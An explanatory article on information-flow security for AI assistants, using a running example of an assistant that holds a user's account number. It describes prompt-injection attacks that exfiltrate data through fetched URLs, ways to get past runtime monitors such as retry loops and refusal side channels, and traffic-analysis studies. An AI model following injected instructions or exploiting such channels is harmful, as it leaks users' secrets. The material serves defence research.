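# Establishing information-flow guarantees for software systems that contain AI models

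## What an information-flow guarantee says

Information-flow security is the part of computer security that deals with where data goes, and what it influences, once a program has it. An information-flow guarantee is a claim that, in a particular system, secret data cannot influence what an unauthorised observer sees, or that untrusted data cannot influence what the system does, beyond what a stated policy allows. The policy states which data may go from which sources to which recipients. Researchers have worked on such guarantees since the 1970s, at first for government and military computers. In the last few years they have turned to software that contains a large language model, a program that generates text by repeatedly predicting what comes next. Developers now connect such models to inboxes, databases and the web.

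Suppose Alice asks her AI assistant to summarise an email from someone who wants her account number. The assistant holds the number, which has eight digits, and can read her inbox and fetch web pages. Apart from the eight digits, this example follows Leaky Summariser, one of 25 small test agents in Dongol's *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026).

### Why access control is not enough

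Most systems protect data by access control, in which a rule for each file or service determines who may open it. Alice's assistant passes all of these checks, because Alice gave it her account number, she wants it to read her email, and assistants ordinarily fetch web pages. But if it fetches a page whose address ends in the eight digits of her account number, the owner of that web server can read them in the server's log, even though the assistant has broken no access rule.

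*A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (Denning, 1976) observed that the access controls of the day governed immediate access to an object but ignored the paths along which information could flow under a whole collection of access rights. *Language-Based Information-Flow Security* (Sabelfeld and Myers, 2003), a survey of three decades of research, likewise notes that access control restricts the release of information but not its propagation. Stricter access rules don't solve the problem, the survey explains, because an owner who relies on access control alone to keep a file secret must grant access only to programs that will never pass the contents on, and identifying those programs is itself an information-flow problem. Encryption is similarly limited, since it protects data on the way to a program but doesn't restrict what the program does after decrypting it.

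### Labels and the lattice

Flow control attaches the restriction to the data, and the restriction stays with the data as it moves. It usually does this with a label that records who may read the data (its confidentiality) or how far its source deserves trust (its integrity). Sabelfeld and Myers credit the security researcher Biba with observing that both properties restrict how information flows. Confidentiality requires that information not flow to the wrong destinations, and integrity requires that it not flow from the wrong sources.

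Confidentiality and integrity are only partly symmetric, because a program can damage the integrity of its results without any outside influence, by computing them incorrectly. A proof that no untrusted source influenced a summary therefore doesn't show that the summary is correct.

Denning gave labels a mathematical model, which consists of a set of security classes, a relation "may flow to" between them (later authors write it ⊑), and a rule for combining classes. If a program computes a value from *a* and *b*, the value gets the *join* of their classes, written *a* ⊔ *b*, which is the lowest class to which both may flow. She derives most of the structure from consistency. If a program may copy *a* into *b* and *b* into *c*, it must also be allowed to copy *a* straight into *c*, or else two permitted steps would produce a forbidden flow. Classes that satisfy her conditions form a lattice,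 an ordered set in which any two elements have a least upper bound and a greatest lower bound. The smallest useful lattice has two classes, public and secret, and forbids only flows from secret to public.

A system like Alice's needs both confidentiality and integrity guarantees. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) combines the order public ⊑ secret with the order trusted ⊑ untrusted, which gives four labels.

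| Label | Example in Alice's assistant | Other labels it may flow to |
|---|---|---|
| trusted, public | the developer's standing instructions | all three |
| trusted, secret | the account number | untrusted, secret |
| untrusted, public | the email, whose author already knows its text | untrusted, secret |
| untrusted, secret | any text that depends on both the number and the email | none |

"Untrusted" stands above "trusted" because using trusted data where untrusted data would suffice is harmless, while using untrusted data where trusted data is needed can cause harm. The two middle labels are incomparable, so neither may flow to the other, and anything that mixes them gets the top label. Labels can also be finer, such as lists of named readers. If A, B and C may read one document and B, C and D may read another, only B and C may read a text that draws on both.

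Access checks can use labels to enforce a flow policy, though crudely. Denning describes two systems of the 1970s that gave each running process a single class. A process could read only from objects whose class may flow to its own, and write only to objects to which its own class may flow. Every flow through the process is therefore permitted. Under this rule, an assistant that is allowed to read Alice's account number can never send a request to the public web, even for a weather forecast. This is safe, but it prevents most of what Alice wanted the assistant to do. Finer methods are of practical interest because they might allow the harmless requests.

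### Noninterference

Data can influence an output without being copied into it. Denning counts a flow whenever information in one place affects the value of information in another, and she distinguishes two kinds. In an *explicit* flow, a program copies or computes data into an output, as when the digits end up in a web address. In an *implicit* flow, the program's next step depends on the data, so the step reveals something about the data. For example, the assistant might fetch one harmless page when the last digit is even and a different harmless page when it is odd. Neither address contains any part of the number, so a filter that searches outgoing traffic for the number finds nothing, but an observer who knows the rule learns whether the last digit is even or odd.

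A definition of security therefore should not depend on a list of ways to leak. *Security Policies and Security Models* (Goguen and Meseguer, 1982) gives one that doesn't, called noninterference. One group of users does not interfere with another if what the first group does with a given set of commands has no effect on what the second group can see. Formally, deleting the first group's uses of those commands from any sequence of commands must not change the output that any member of the second group gets.

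Later authors recast the idea for programs with secret inputs. They compare two runs that differ only in the secret. Write *l* for the public inputs, *s* for the secret, and view(*l*, *s*) for everything the observer sees when the system runs on them. Noninterference is then the requirement

$$\text{for all } l,\ s_1,\ s_2:\quad \mathrm{view}(l, s_1) = \mathrm{view}(l, s_2).$$

In Alice's case, *s* is her account number and *l* is all the other input, including her request and the text of the email. The view is whatever reaches the email's author, such as requests to a web server the author runs.

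"For all *l*" covers every email that anyone could write, so the formula needs no separate clause about attackers. Dongol explains that for an agent, this means nothing the attacker receives depends on the user's data, whatever content the attacker sends. "For all *s*" covers the hundred million possible account numbers. The claim is false if even one email and one pair of numbers produce different views. Finding equal views for a thousand emails would not prove it, because it covers every possible email. Because the claim compares runs with one another, it is a hyperproperty, a requirement on the whole set of a system's executions.

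The integrity version requires that changing the untrusted inputs, while the trusted ones stay fixed, does not change the system's actions. This requirement depends on which outputs count as actions. Alice's summary should change with the email, since it would otherwise be useless, but she may reasonably demand that the assistant's web requests stay the same.

Language models usually choose their words at random from a probability distribution, so two runs on identical inputs can differ. *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) starts from the standard approach of comparing the distributions of what the observer sees, rather than single outcomes. Suppose the assistant fetches some page in 10% of runs when the account number begins with 1, and in 20% of runs otherwise. A single run can't settle whether the first digit is 1, because the fetch can occur either way, but someone who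 watches many runs can work it out, and the definition rightly counts this as a leak. The paper's theorem is slightly weaker than equality of distributions because it lets the secret influence whether a run finishes, which is a common concession in the field.

Full noninterference is too strict for many useful assistants, which have to release some secrets on purpose. Such a deliberate release is called declassification. A policy can name these exceptions, so the guarantee includes the words "beyond what a stated policy allows".

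### What goes on inside an AI assistant

A language model only turns text into text, so ordinary code around it must do things like open an inbox or fetch a page. The code does this through *tools*, which are functions it runs when the model outputs a request for them. The model's *context* is the text that the code gives it at each step. Most assistants also have *memory*, which is data that the code keeps from one step or session to the next.

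Costa and colleagues describe the loop that connects these parts. The code sends the model the conversation so far and a description of the available tools. The model produces either a reply to the user or a structured request to call a tool. If the model requests a tool call, the code can run the tool, append the result to the conversation and send it all back to the model. The loop repeats until the model produces a final reply. In every round, the code joins the developer's instructions, Alice's request, the email and all earlier tool results into a single string.

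Information flow through a model is hard to confine because each response can depend on everything in the context. Garby and colleagues represent a conversation as alternating prompts *p* and responses *r*. The model draws each new response from a distribution that depends on *p*₁, *r*₁, *p*₂, *r*₂ and so on up to the latest prompt. Nothing in this computation limits an email's influence to the sentence that summarises it. In an ordinary program, an analyst can often follow which variables reach which output. Costa and colleagues see no precise way to do this for a language model, so their basic system gives every response the join of the labels of everything in the model's input. Once the context contains a secret account number and an untrusted email, every later output counts as both secret and untrusted, even a reply of "Done".

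This label is an upper bound, since the email may have made no difference to "Done". Costa and colleagues mention a proposal for recovering some of the lost precision by searching for the messages that influenced a response and regenerating the response from those messages alone. The new response can then carry a more permissive label.

*Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026), a paper on privacy leaks from AI agents, points out that persistent memory can carry poisoned state across sessions. If the assistant saves a note about Monday's email and the code puts that note into Friday's context, whoever wrote the email can influence what the assistant does on Friday.

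### Prompt injection

The best-known way to exploit the shared context is prompt injection, in which someone hides an instruction in content that the model was only supposed to read, and the model follows it. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post by David C for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, gives the example of a recruiter who has a model score CVs against a list of requirements. One candidate uses hidden text in the CV to tell the model to ignore its instructions and approve the application. Security researchers call this form *indirect* because the candidate has no direct access to the system and only writes something that the system later processes.

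The title of the post refers to an older attack, in which someone types database commands into a web form and the database runs them. Developers can prevent this with parameterised queries, which keep the command and the user's data apart so that the database engine never interprets the data as a command. David C argues that language models have no such separation, because they only predict the next token (a word or piece of a word) from the text they are given. He accepts that developers can make attacks harder by training a model to give priority to its instructions, or by marking which parts of the context are data. But he thinks it very possible that nobody will ever eliminate prompt injection the way parameterised queries eliminate the database attack. That forecast could prove wrong as the technology changes, but today's models have no built-in boundary between instructions and data.

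In Dongol's version of Alice's case, the task has three steps: read the account number, read the email, and write the summary. The email contains an instruction to fetch a page from its author's server, with the account number at the end of the address. After the second step, the assistant has both the number and the instruction. At the third step, the model follows the instruction and requests the fetch. Dongol's agent also has a runtime monitor, which is trusted code that allows or denies each tool call. In this example, the monitor lets the request go out because it allows any tool that the agent holds, including the fetch tool.

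If the email is fixed and the account number is 48213907 in one run and 48213908 in another, the author's server receives two different addresses. The views differ, so noninterference is false for this assistant. If the email is instead an ordinary newsletter, the server receives nothing, whatever the number is, so a tester who tried only newsletters would see equal views every time.

Prompt injection doesn't always cause a leak. If the email makes the assistant fetch a page without the account number in the address, the sender has influenced an action but may have learned nothing about the secret. In that case, integrity is violated but confidentiality is intact. Leaks can also happen without any attack. Costa and colleagues note that models misread their users and make unnecessary tool calls even when all the data is trustworthy. If an assistant looks up Alice's bank by pasting her account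 number into a public search engine, it leaks the number to the search engine's operator. Noninterference with respect to that operator fails, just as it would if a thief's email had caused the leak.

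## Stating the system boundary and the adversary

The search engine's operator and the email's author see different parts of what Alice's assistant does, so the assistant can be secure against one and still leak to the other. Anyone who claims a guarantee therefore has to define the system boundary and the adversary model before gathering evidence. The *system boundary* separates the components and channels that the claim covers from those it doesn't. The *adversary model* is a description of what the attacker can see, control and know. Noninterference doesn't specify either. It requires equal views for any two secrets, but somebody has to decide what the view includes, and "for all *l*" covers only the inputs they identified.

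### Listing the components and channels

Alice's assistant includes the app on her phone, the code that runs the loop, the runtime monitor, the language model (often on another company's servers), the inbox and fetch tools, the storage for memory and logs, and the networks that connect them. The list should also include things developers rarely think of as part of it, such as a script that restarts a failed task.

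The next step is to list every channel out of these components, meaning every way something inside them could affect what an outsider sees. The list includes channels meant to carry data, such as web requests and emails, and *side channels*, which are observable effects that nobody meant to carry data, such as timing, packet size and refusals. Each channel then gets one of three marks. It is *covered* if the evidence for the claim takes it into account, *assumed safe* if the claim relies on a stated fact about it that still has to be established, and *excluded* if the claim does not apply to it.

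The claim loses its support if an assumption is false. A leak through an excluded channel doesn't make the claim false, but it still exposes Alice's account number.

Suppose a developer wants to claim that the email's author, who also runs a web server, can learn nothing about the account number from the content and order of the messages and web requests that the assistant sends. An inventory for that claim might look like this.

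| Channel | How the account number could get out | Mark |
|---|---|---|
| Tool calls and their arguments | the assistant emails the number to the author | covered |
| Fetched addresses | the digits appear in the address, or decide which page the assistant fetches | covered |
| Replies to Alice | a reply contains an image that her app loads from the author's server | assumed safe: the app loads nothing from outside |
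| Refusals and error messages | an error message shows which request the monitor denied | assumed safe: no outsider sees a denial |
| Logs | a shared log records a denied address in full | assumed safe: only the operator reads the logs |
| Memory kept between sessions | a saved note brings the email's instruction back when the assistant next handles the number | assumed safe: every session starts empty |
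| Retries | the number decides how many attempts a task takes | assumed safe: nothing restarts a failed task |
| Caches | the model's provider answers faster if it has recently processed the same text | excluded |
| Timing | the number decides when a request goes out | excluded |
| Packet size | the number affects the length of an encrypted reply | excluded |

Several of these assumptions follow Dongol, whose theorems apply only to deployments that meet seven conditions. A trusted interpreter must run the plan, so the model can't skip or alter steps. Every tool call and every read of untrusted content must go through the monitor, which decides on them one at a time. Untrusted text may enter the model's context only after the monitor has allowed the read. A denied request must have no effect the attacker can see. The attacker must see neither the monitor's state nor the agent's internal steps,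 so displaying a reply must not load an image. A new session must clear everything the model retains from untrusted content. The attacker must not be able to write to any source the system treats as trusted, so a calendar that accepts invitations from strangers can't be a trusted source.

Some of these conditions are easy to meet. Test software satisfies the two conditions about the monitor if it checks every call and fetch before executing it. But an agent that drives a web browser outside the monitor's control violates those two conditions, and a memory feature that retrieves text from old sessions violates the condition about new sessions.

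A monitor's refusals can leak private information, which is easy to overlook because a refusal looks like the monitor doing its job. In Dongol's Permission Probe, a user's private setting determines whether the agent may use a certain internal tool, and an injected instruction makes the agent try that tool. The attacker cannot see the agent's tool calls, but if an error message reveals which tool the monitor refused, the attacker learns the setting.

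Caches can reveal one customer's prompts to another when they share the same machines. *Whisper Leak* (McDonald and Bar Or, 2025) describes an attack by Zheng and colleagues in which the attacker sends guesses at other users' prompts and times the answers. A fast answer suggests that someone else recently sent the same or similar text. Alice's monitor and tools would not detect the attack, because the whole exchange takes place between the attacker and the provider.

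### A monitor inside a retry loop

The row for retries matters because a system with a correct monitor can still leak everything. Garby and colleagues give an example from CaMeL, a defence in which one model writes a program for the user's task and an interpreter runs it. The interpreter tracks labels and checks a policy before each tool call. When a run fails, ordinary Python code outside the interpreter starts another attempt, and this code does not track labels.

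Suppose an attacker gets the assistant to run a program that tries something forbidden only if Alice's account number is at least 50,000,000. The monitor blocks the program in that case and otherwise lets it finish. An observer who learns whether the run finished therefore learns one bit of information about the account number. Garby and colleagues regard a one-bit leak as unremarkable because the usual guarantees, including their own theorem, permit it by design.

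However, the loop can repeat the question with a different threshold. Each attempt starts with clean labels, even though the code that starts it has received the previous attempt's outcome. Garby and colleagues point out that a driver that adapts each run to earlier answers can extract the entire secret, one bit at a time.

For an eight-digit number this doesn't take long. There are 10⁸ possible values, and

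$$\log_2 10^8 \approx 26.6,$$

so 27 yes-or-no answers are enough. If the number is 48213907, the first run finishes, because the number is below 50,000,000. The next four runs test 25,000,000, then 37,500,000, 43,750,000 and 46,875,000, and the monitor blocks all of them. These five answers narrow a hundred million candidates to 3,125,000. Another 22 answers leave only one.

This calculation assumes that the attacker can influence the program in every attempt, and that the driver continues after a run that finishes. A plain retry loop stops at its first success, so an observer learns only how many attempts failed. With a limit of 27 attempts, that count has 28 possible values and carries less than five bits. But the limit applies to each task separately, so more of the secret can leak over repeated tasks, and Alice may use the assistant every day.

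Within each run, the secret still influences only whether the run finishes, so the claim about the monitor holds. But the claim about the assistant is false, because two account numbers can produce different sequences of blocked and finished runs. The attacker may not need to watch those runs, since a later attempt has clean labels and could send out what the loop has found. According to Garby and colleagues, CaMeL's developers acknowledge this channel and reduce it by censoring what one attempt passes to the next, but without a formal guarantee.

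The remedy is to move the boundary so that it encloses the loop. Garby and colleagues wrote an agent whose loop runs entirely inside a language that tracks labels. The agent first tests its program on artificial data, where it can fail and retry without touching private data, and it sees the real data only once the program works. But if someone restarts the agent by hand, those restarts still form a loop outside the boundary, so a claim that allows a leak of one bit per run should specify the number of runs allowed.

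### What the adversary sees, controls and can cause

Dongol describes an adversary by what it observes, how it controls the model, and what an instruction can do once the model follows it. A defence that is secure under one combination of these may leak information under another.

An attacker can observe the system at one of three levels. An *event-level* attacker sees the allowed calls to the tools visible to it, including their arguments and order. In Alice's case, these are the messages and requests that reach the email's author. A *step-level* attacker also sees when each step happens, as someone timing the assistant's replies would. An attacker *with views* can also see some refusals, or when the agent reads from a server that the attacker runs.

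Noninterference compares every pair of runs that differ only in the secret, but Dongol's event-level definition compares two runs only if the same number of calls reach the attacker between one read and the next. Suppose an injected instruction makes the assistant fetch a permitted page if a secret bit is 0 and a forbidden page if it is 1, then send a fixed completion message. The instruction's author receives both the page request and the completion message if the bit is 0, but only the completion message if it is 1. A server owner could learn the bit by counting messages, but the event-level definition never compares these runs, so the difference does not count as a leak. A developer who uses this definition should state separately whether the attacker's view includes the number of messages.

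The step-level definition does detect this leak, but it compares only runs that have the same length and read at the same steps. If a secret bit makes the agent take one extra internal step, and an injection then sends that bit to the attacker, the definition never compares runs with different bits, so the agent counts as secure. A proof of security against an attacker who sees timing therefore doesn't automatically cover an attacker who sees only content. Dongol proves that the two definitions give the same verdict when, roughly, the pattern of visible events depends only on what the attacker does.

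The second axis is control of the model. The attacker writes the email but doesn't run the model, and nobody can predict which text a given model will obey. Dongol therefore lets the attacker choose two functions. The *parser* determines which pieces of text count as instructions and what call each one requests, and the *oracle* determines when the model obeys. The resulting call may use anything in the agent's memory, including the secrets. Marking untrusted text and asking the model to ignore instructions in it achieves nothing against this adversary, who can choose a parser that treats marked text as instructions anyway. The marking helps only under the added assumption that the model ignores instructions in marked text.

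The only limit on the attacker's choice is that the oracle must follow a schedule fixed in advance, so the model can't decide whether to obey based on a secret or the monitor's response. This restriction matters because an agent that is refused may well try something else. Dongol leaves models that can react in these ways to future work.

A single combination of parser and oracle is enough to prove a leak, because the attacker may choose that combination. A claim of security against this adversary must cover every combination that the adversary model allows. Some of Dongol's verdicts cover them all, while others cover only the one injection in the example, so they support very different claims.

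The third axis is the effect of an obeyed instruction. In the simplest case, the instruction causes one tool call that the plan doesn't contain, such as the fetch in Alice's example. It may instead run a whole program, which can leak data without making a tool call. For example, the program can write the account number into a variable that the plan later sends to the email's author. Running injected programs in a sandbox that discards their changes prevents this.

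Some systems keep untrusted text away from the planning model and let a second, *quarantined* model answer questions about that text. An injection can then corrupt only the answers. But if the quarantined model can read Alice's notes as well as the email, it can quote the notes in an answer that the plan sends out.

### Call Approval

Call Approval, one of Dongol's examples, shows how much a verdict can depend on observation alone. An assistant reads an email, Alice approves the exact text of a reply, and the assistant sends it. The monitor allows an outgoing message only if it matches the approved text, and each approval covers one message. The email contains an instruction to send Alice's account number. The model obeys this instruction after Alice approves the reply but before the assistant sends it.

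Exact approval is stricter than Tool Approval, under which Alice's approval permits the next message, whatever its contents. Under Tool Approval, the injected call sends the private data to the attacker and uses up the approval, so Alice's own reply is never sent. Under exact approval, the outcome depends on whether the account number happens to equal the approved reply.

| | Number differs from the reply | Number equals the reply |
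|---|---|---|
| The injected message | the monitor denies it | the monitor allows it, and it uses up the approval |
| The planned reply | the monitor allows it | the monitor denies it |
| What the email's author receives | one message containing the reply | the same message, one step earlier |

Someone who sees only message content gets the same text in both cases and learns nothing about the account number, but someone who can also tell that the message came a step early learns that the number equals the reply. Dongol proves that the agent is secure at the event level, for injected instructions that send messages and a model that doesn't obey them forever, and that it leaks at the step level.

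The size of the leak depends on the secret. If the secret is a random account number, the test is almost always negative and rules out only one of a hundred million possible values. If the secret is whether Alice will accept an offer, and she approves the reply "yes", one test reveals the answer. The claim "secure with exact approval" is therefore true for some observers and false for others of the same software.

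### What FIDES trusts

FIDES, the agent that Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft to enforce policies on labelled data, uses a different adversary model. They assume that user messages, the language models, the developer's instructions and the tool descriptions are all trusted and public. Their adversary can tamper with data that tools obtain from untrusted sources, and can observe the effects of certain tool calls. A public web search, for instance, returns untrusted text and may also appear in a website's visitor statistics. The adversary cannot directly observe what the agent sends to the model or what the model returns.

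These assumptions have consequences that Alice might not expect. If she types her account number into her request, FIDES treats it as public because it arrived in a user message. FIDES labels the number secret only if it comes from a source that somebody has labelled secret. If she copies a suspicious email into the chat instead of letting the assistant open it, FIDES treats the text as trusted. An outside company could also supply a tool with an instruction hidden in its description, which researchers call *tool poisoning*. A claim that rests on either Costa and colleagues' assumptions or Dongol's doesn't cover this attack.

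The two models differ in other respects. Dongol assumes that the attacker cannot answer a tool call, so his theorems exclude an attacker who runs the assistant's search engine, reads a query containing Alice's data and tailors the results to it. Costa and colleagues expect tool results to contain text that the adversary has written. Dongol also requires a plan made before the agent reads anything untrusted, so his theorems don't apply to assistants built on the ordinary agent loop, in which the AI model chooses every call. Costa and colleagues model assistants of this kind.

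Results proved under one model don't transfer to the other, though neither model is wrong. Both also omit what someone on the network can infer from the size and timing of encrypted traffic. Dongol puts side channels out of scope, and Costa and colleagues assume only that nobody reads the AI model's queries and responses directly.

### What encrypted traffic reveals

Most chat services *stream* their answers, sending each token or small group of tokens as soon as the model produces it. TLS, the standard encryption for web traffic, hides the content of each piece but adds only a small constant to its length. Anyone who can watch the connection, such as an internet provider or the owner of a café's Wi-Fi, can therefore see a sequence of sizes and arrival times that depends on the answer. McDonald and Bar Or, both at Microsoft, measured how much an eavesdropper could learn from this sequence.

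The study tested whether such a sequence reveals that a user is asking about one topic, the legality of money laundering. The two researchers used a model to write 100 versions of the question, sent each version 100 times to each of 28 commercial models, and mixed in 11,716 unrelated questions from Quora. They inserted random spaces so that caching wouldn't distort the timings. They trained classifiers on the recorded sizes and times, holding back 20 of the 100 versions for testing.

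McDonald and Bar Or scored each classifier by a measure that combines precision (the share of flagged conversations that are on the topic) with recall (the share of on-topic conversations that it flags). A perfect score is 100%, and they put random guessing at 50%. The best classifier scored above 97% for 17 of the 28 models. They say it scored above 98% for those 17, but their results show this for only 12. The lowest score was 71.2%, for one of Amazon's models. For most models, packet sizes alone were enough.

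For mass surveillance, the study estimates that if one conversation in about 10,000 were relevant, an eavesdropper could catch 5% to 20% of the relevant ones with no false alarms for 17 models. The study warns that this is an extrapolation, and it is a large one. Even if a classifier raised no false alarms on the 11,716 unrelated questions, its true false-alarm rate could be as high as about one in 4,000. At that rate it would raise two or three false alarms for every relevant conversation in the traffic. The study does show that a conversation's topic affects what an eavesdropper sees, which is enough to refute noninterference for an observer on the network.

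The measurements also predate the fixes. McDonald and Bar Or notified the providers in June 2025, and by October OpenAI, xAI, Mistral and Microsoft had added defences, while some other providers declined or never replied. The defences that McDonald and Bar Or tested helped only partly. Adding random padding to each piece lowered the score for one model from 97.5% to 92.9%. Sending tokens in groups of five lowered it from 98.2% to 94.8% for another model, but worked much better for most others.

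A newer study suggests that the problem isn't specific to one topic or a few services. Pouryousef, Lopez and colleagues (2026), in *A Large-Scale Benchmark and Risk Assessment of Traffic Analysis Attacks*, ran ten open models on their own server and sent each model 60 prompts, 100 times apiece. Their classifier used only the traffic from the model to the user. On prompts that weren't in its training data, it identified which of six kinds of prompt the user had sent (a request for code or for a summary, for example) in 67.4% of cases, compared with 16.7% for guessing.

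They also recorded teams of two to five agents working on ten kinds of task. The classifier identified the task from the traffic between the agents and their model about 85% of the time, compared with 10% for guessing. It was still right 54% to 59% of the time when they removed everything about packet size and volume, so padding alone would not hide what the agents were doing. These conditions favour an attacker, who has examples of every possible answer and knows where each conversation begins and ends. Accuracy fell from 83% to 52% when the researchers trained the classifier on teams organised in one way and tested it on teams organised in another.

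None of this recovers Alice's account number. Every eight-digit number has the same length, so packet sizes probably reveal little about the digits. The traffic is more likely to show that she is discussing her bank account, or what her assistant is doing. *ANT* (2026), a collection of traffic recorded from AI agents, links bursts of network activity to the start of each stage of an agent's work. In a typical stage, the agent calls the model, calls a tool and reads the result. If an eavesdropper can pick out those stages reliably, the step-level attacker in Call Approval is realistic.

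To mark packet size and timing as covered, a developer has to make the traffic look the same whatever the assistant is doing. McDonald and Bar Or describe the strong form of this defence, which pads every packet to a uniform size and sends packets at a fixed rate. This uses more bandwidth and slows the answers down, so most developers will mark these channels as excluded. They should then state in the claim that it doesn't cover the eavesdropper.

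## Stating which flows are allowed

Noninterference forbids even disclosures that Alice wants, as Dongol shows with a calendar assistant that answers meeting requests. Suppose Bob emails to ask whether Alice can meet on Thursday at three. A useful reply has to depend on her calendar, and noninterference forbids that dependence however good the monitor is.

Researchers have several ways of stating which disclosures to permit, and each overlooks different leaks.

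### Declassification

The most direct way is to write down each deliberate release. Sabelfeld and Sands, in *Declassification: Dimensions and Principles* (2009), sort such policies by four questions: what information the system releases, who releases it, where in the system the release happens, and when. For Alice's calendar, the answers might be:

- **What:** her free hours on the day in question, but not the names of her appointments.
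- **Who:** Alice, through a standing instruction, and not the author of an email.
- **Where:** only the step that replies to a meeting request.
- **When:** only after such a request has arrived.

A policy that answers only some of these questions permits more than it seems to. If Alice specifies only what the assistant may release, a hidden instruction in a newsletter could make it send her free hours to a stranger every morning without breaking the policy. If she specifies only where it may release information, the reply to Bob could include her medical appointments.

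The drawback is that somebody has to answer the questions for every task, because a release that suits a meeting request is wrong for a newsletter summary. Dongol also objects that such a policy describes what the agent may release but not what a prompt injection adds.

FlowSeal, the defence proposed in *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow*, spreads out the work of stating which flows are allowed by consulting the data's owner about particular releases as they come up. Its code tracks which protected records the agent has read and intercepts every message or document the agent tries to send out. If the owner has authorised the recipient to have those records, the text goes out. If the recipient is unknown, a separate language model compares the text with the protected records and labels it "safe" or "blocked". The agent can then send the owner a request to release particular records to that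 recipient for a stated purpose.

The paper proves that no text derived from a protected record reaches an unauthorised recipient unless the checking model wrongly answers "safe". The proof doesn't limit how often the model makes this mistake, so the error rate has to be measured by testing. The paper calls the check declassification, but its purpose is to clear text that contains nothing secret. The owner's authorisation is the step that deliberately releases a secret. In the paper's tests, agents with FlowSeal completed 72.4% of harmless tasks, compared with 75.9% for the best prompt-based defence.

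### Permitted leakage

The question of what a system may release has a mathematical form. Choose a function δ that maps each secret to the part of it that the observer may learn, and compare only runs that agree on that part:

$$\text{for all } l,\ s_1,\ s_2:\quad \delta(s_1) = \delta(s_2)\ \Rightarrow\ \mathrm{view}(l, s_1) = \mathrm{view}(l, s_2).$$

Dongol calls this a *disclosure bound*. If δ gives the same value for every secret, the formula is ordinary noninterference. If δ(*s*) = *s*, the formula permits everything, because it only compares each secret with itself.

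Suppose a shop that owes Alice a refund needs the last four digits of her account number. Since δ(48213907) = δ(60553907) = 3907, the shop must see the same thing whichever of these numbers is hers. A reply containing "3907" meets this requirement. A web request with all eight digits in its address violates it, because the address would be different for each number. The requirement doesn't apply to the pair 48213907 and 48213908, because their last four digits differ and the shop is allowed to learn those digits.

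The policy has let the shop narrow a hundred million candidates to ten thousand. Separate permissions can also combine to reveal more than anyone intended. If another company may learn the first four digits, the assistant can comply with both policies and still give the two companies the whole number between them. The formula also doesn't account for why information is released or who prompted the release.

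Alpay and Alpay (2026), in *AgentSecBench*, adapt the idea to prompt injection by varying the untrusted text instead of the secret. They choose a "bad" event, such as a forbidden tool call, and compare text *O* written by an attacker with harmless text *O*₀ that gives the agent the same permitted information. The agent meets their definition if, for every attacker with realistic computing power,

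$$\big|\Pr[\text{bad} \mid O] - \Pr[\text{bad} \mid O_0]\big| \le \varepsilon.$$

The tolerance ε allows for the randomness of language models, but even a small ε can matter. If harmless emails never cause the bad event and ε is 0.01, a malicious email could cause it up to 1% of the time. An attacker who sends a thousand such emails could expect up to ten successes.

The definition also covers only events that someone has specified as bad. Alpay and Alpay define leakage of a secret separately, as the information the agent's response carries about the secret beyond what the permitted information already reveals.

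### Robust declassification

Permitted leakage limits what the assistant releases, but an attacker may still choose when to trigger the release. *Robust declassification*, which Zdancewic and Myers proposed in 2001, forbids untrusted input to influence what a system releases. Write *e* and *e*′ for two emails and hold all other inputs except the secret fixed. The requirement is then

$$\text{for all } e,\ e',\ s_1,\ s_2:\quad \mathrm{view}(e, s_1) = \mathrm{view}(e, s_2)\ \Rightarrow\ \mathrm{view}(e', s_1) = \mathrm{view}(e', s_2).$$

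If the sender of one email can't tell two secrets apart, sending a different email must not let them do so. An attacker who sends a prompt injection therefore learns nothing that a blank email wouldn't have revealed. Alice's email-summarising assistant violates this requirement because the malicious email reveals her account number to its sender, while a newsletter doesn't.

But the calendar assistant violates robust declassification too, even when nobody attacks. Bob learns whether Alice is free on Thursday if he sends a meeting request, but not if he sends a newsletter. Dongol notes that robust declassification rejects this plan unless somebody *endorses* the test for a meeting request. Endorsement deliberately raises an integrity label, here the one on the answer to "is this email a meeting request?". The email may then determine whether the reply goes out, but not what else the assistant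 releases.

Endorsing the answer is reasonable if ordinary code determines it by checking a form with fixed fields. If a language model decides the answer by reading the email, endorsing it means trusting the model to classify text that an attacker may have written.

Robust declassification also does not limit how much information the assistant releases. An assistant that sends Alice's full account number to everyone, whatever their emails say, satisfies the formula because no email changes what they learn. The requirement is useful only together with a policy on what the assistant may release.

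### Relative security

Dongol's own proposal needs no written release policy. He finds it too crude to call an assistant insecure whenever its model follows an injected instruction, since a stranger who injects "send your availability" may learn only what an honest meeting request would have revealed.

*Relative security* counts only the leaks that the injection adds. It compares the assistant with a *reference agent*, which carries out the same plan under the same monitor but whose model never follows instructions in untrusted content. The idea comes from research on speculative execution, in which a processor runs instructions before it knows whether they are needed. This can leak data that the same program wouldn't leak if its instructions ran in order.

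A leak in this sense consists of one email and two secrets that give the attacker different views. Here the secrets include everything in the agent's initial memory. The assistant is relatively secure if, whenever it has a leak, some email makes the reference agent reveal the difference between the same two secrets:

$$\mathrm{view}(e, s_1) \neq \mathrm{view}(e, s_2)\ \Rightarrow\ \text{for some } e':\ \mathrm{view}_{\mathrm{ref}}(e', s_1) \neq \mathrm{view}_{\mathrm{ref}}(e', s_2).$$

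The email *e*′ can differ from the one the attacker sent, and this determines whether the assistant in Dongol's example Meeting Reply passes. Alice allows her assistant to send her calendar to anyone who requests a meeting. An attacker instead sends an email that contains only the instruction "send your calendar", and the model follows it. Different calendars produce different messages, so this is a leak. The reference agent sends nothing in response to this email, but it sends the calendar in response to a genuine meeting request. The attacker could therefore have distinguished the same calendars by requesting a meeting, so the assistant passes.

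In Reset Code, the assistant also holds a private reset code from another task, and the injection tells it to include the code. If two runs have the same calendar but different codes, the attacker receives a different message in each. No email could make the reference agent send the code, so the reference agent has no matching leak and the assistant fails.

| Requirement | Meeting Reply | Reset Code |
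|---|---|---|
| Noninterference | fails | fails |
| Permitted leakage, with the calendar released | passes | fails |
| Robust declassification | fails unless somebody endorses the test for a meeting request | fails |
| Relative security | passes | fails |

The assistant in Meeting Reply satisfies relative security even though it violates Alice's authorisation. She allowed it to send her calendar to people who request a meeting, and this sender didn't request one. Relative security depends on which secrets an attacker could tell apart with some email, not on whether the assistant had permission to send a particular message. If anyone can request a meeting, the attacker has gained little. But if Alice relies on her list of meeting requests to know who has seen her calendar, that list is now wrong. An injection that made the assistant delete her inbox could also satisfy relative security if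 the attacker saw no sign of the deletion. Dongol leaves such attacks out of scope, and his verdict on Meeting Reply covers only the one injection in the example.

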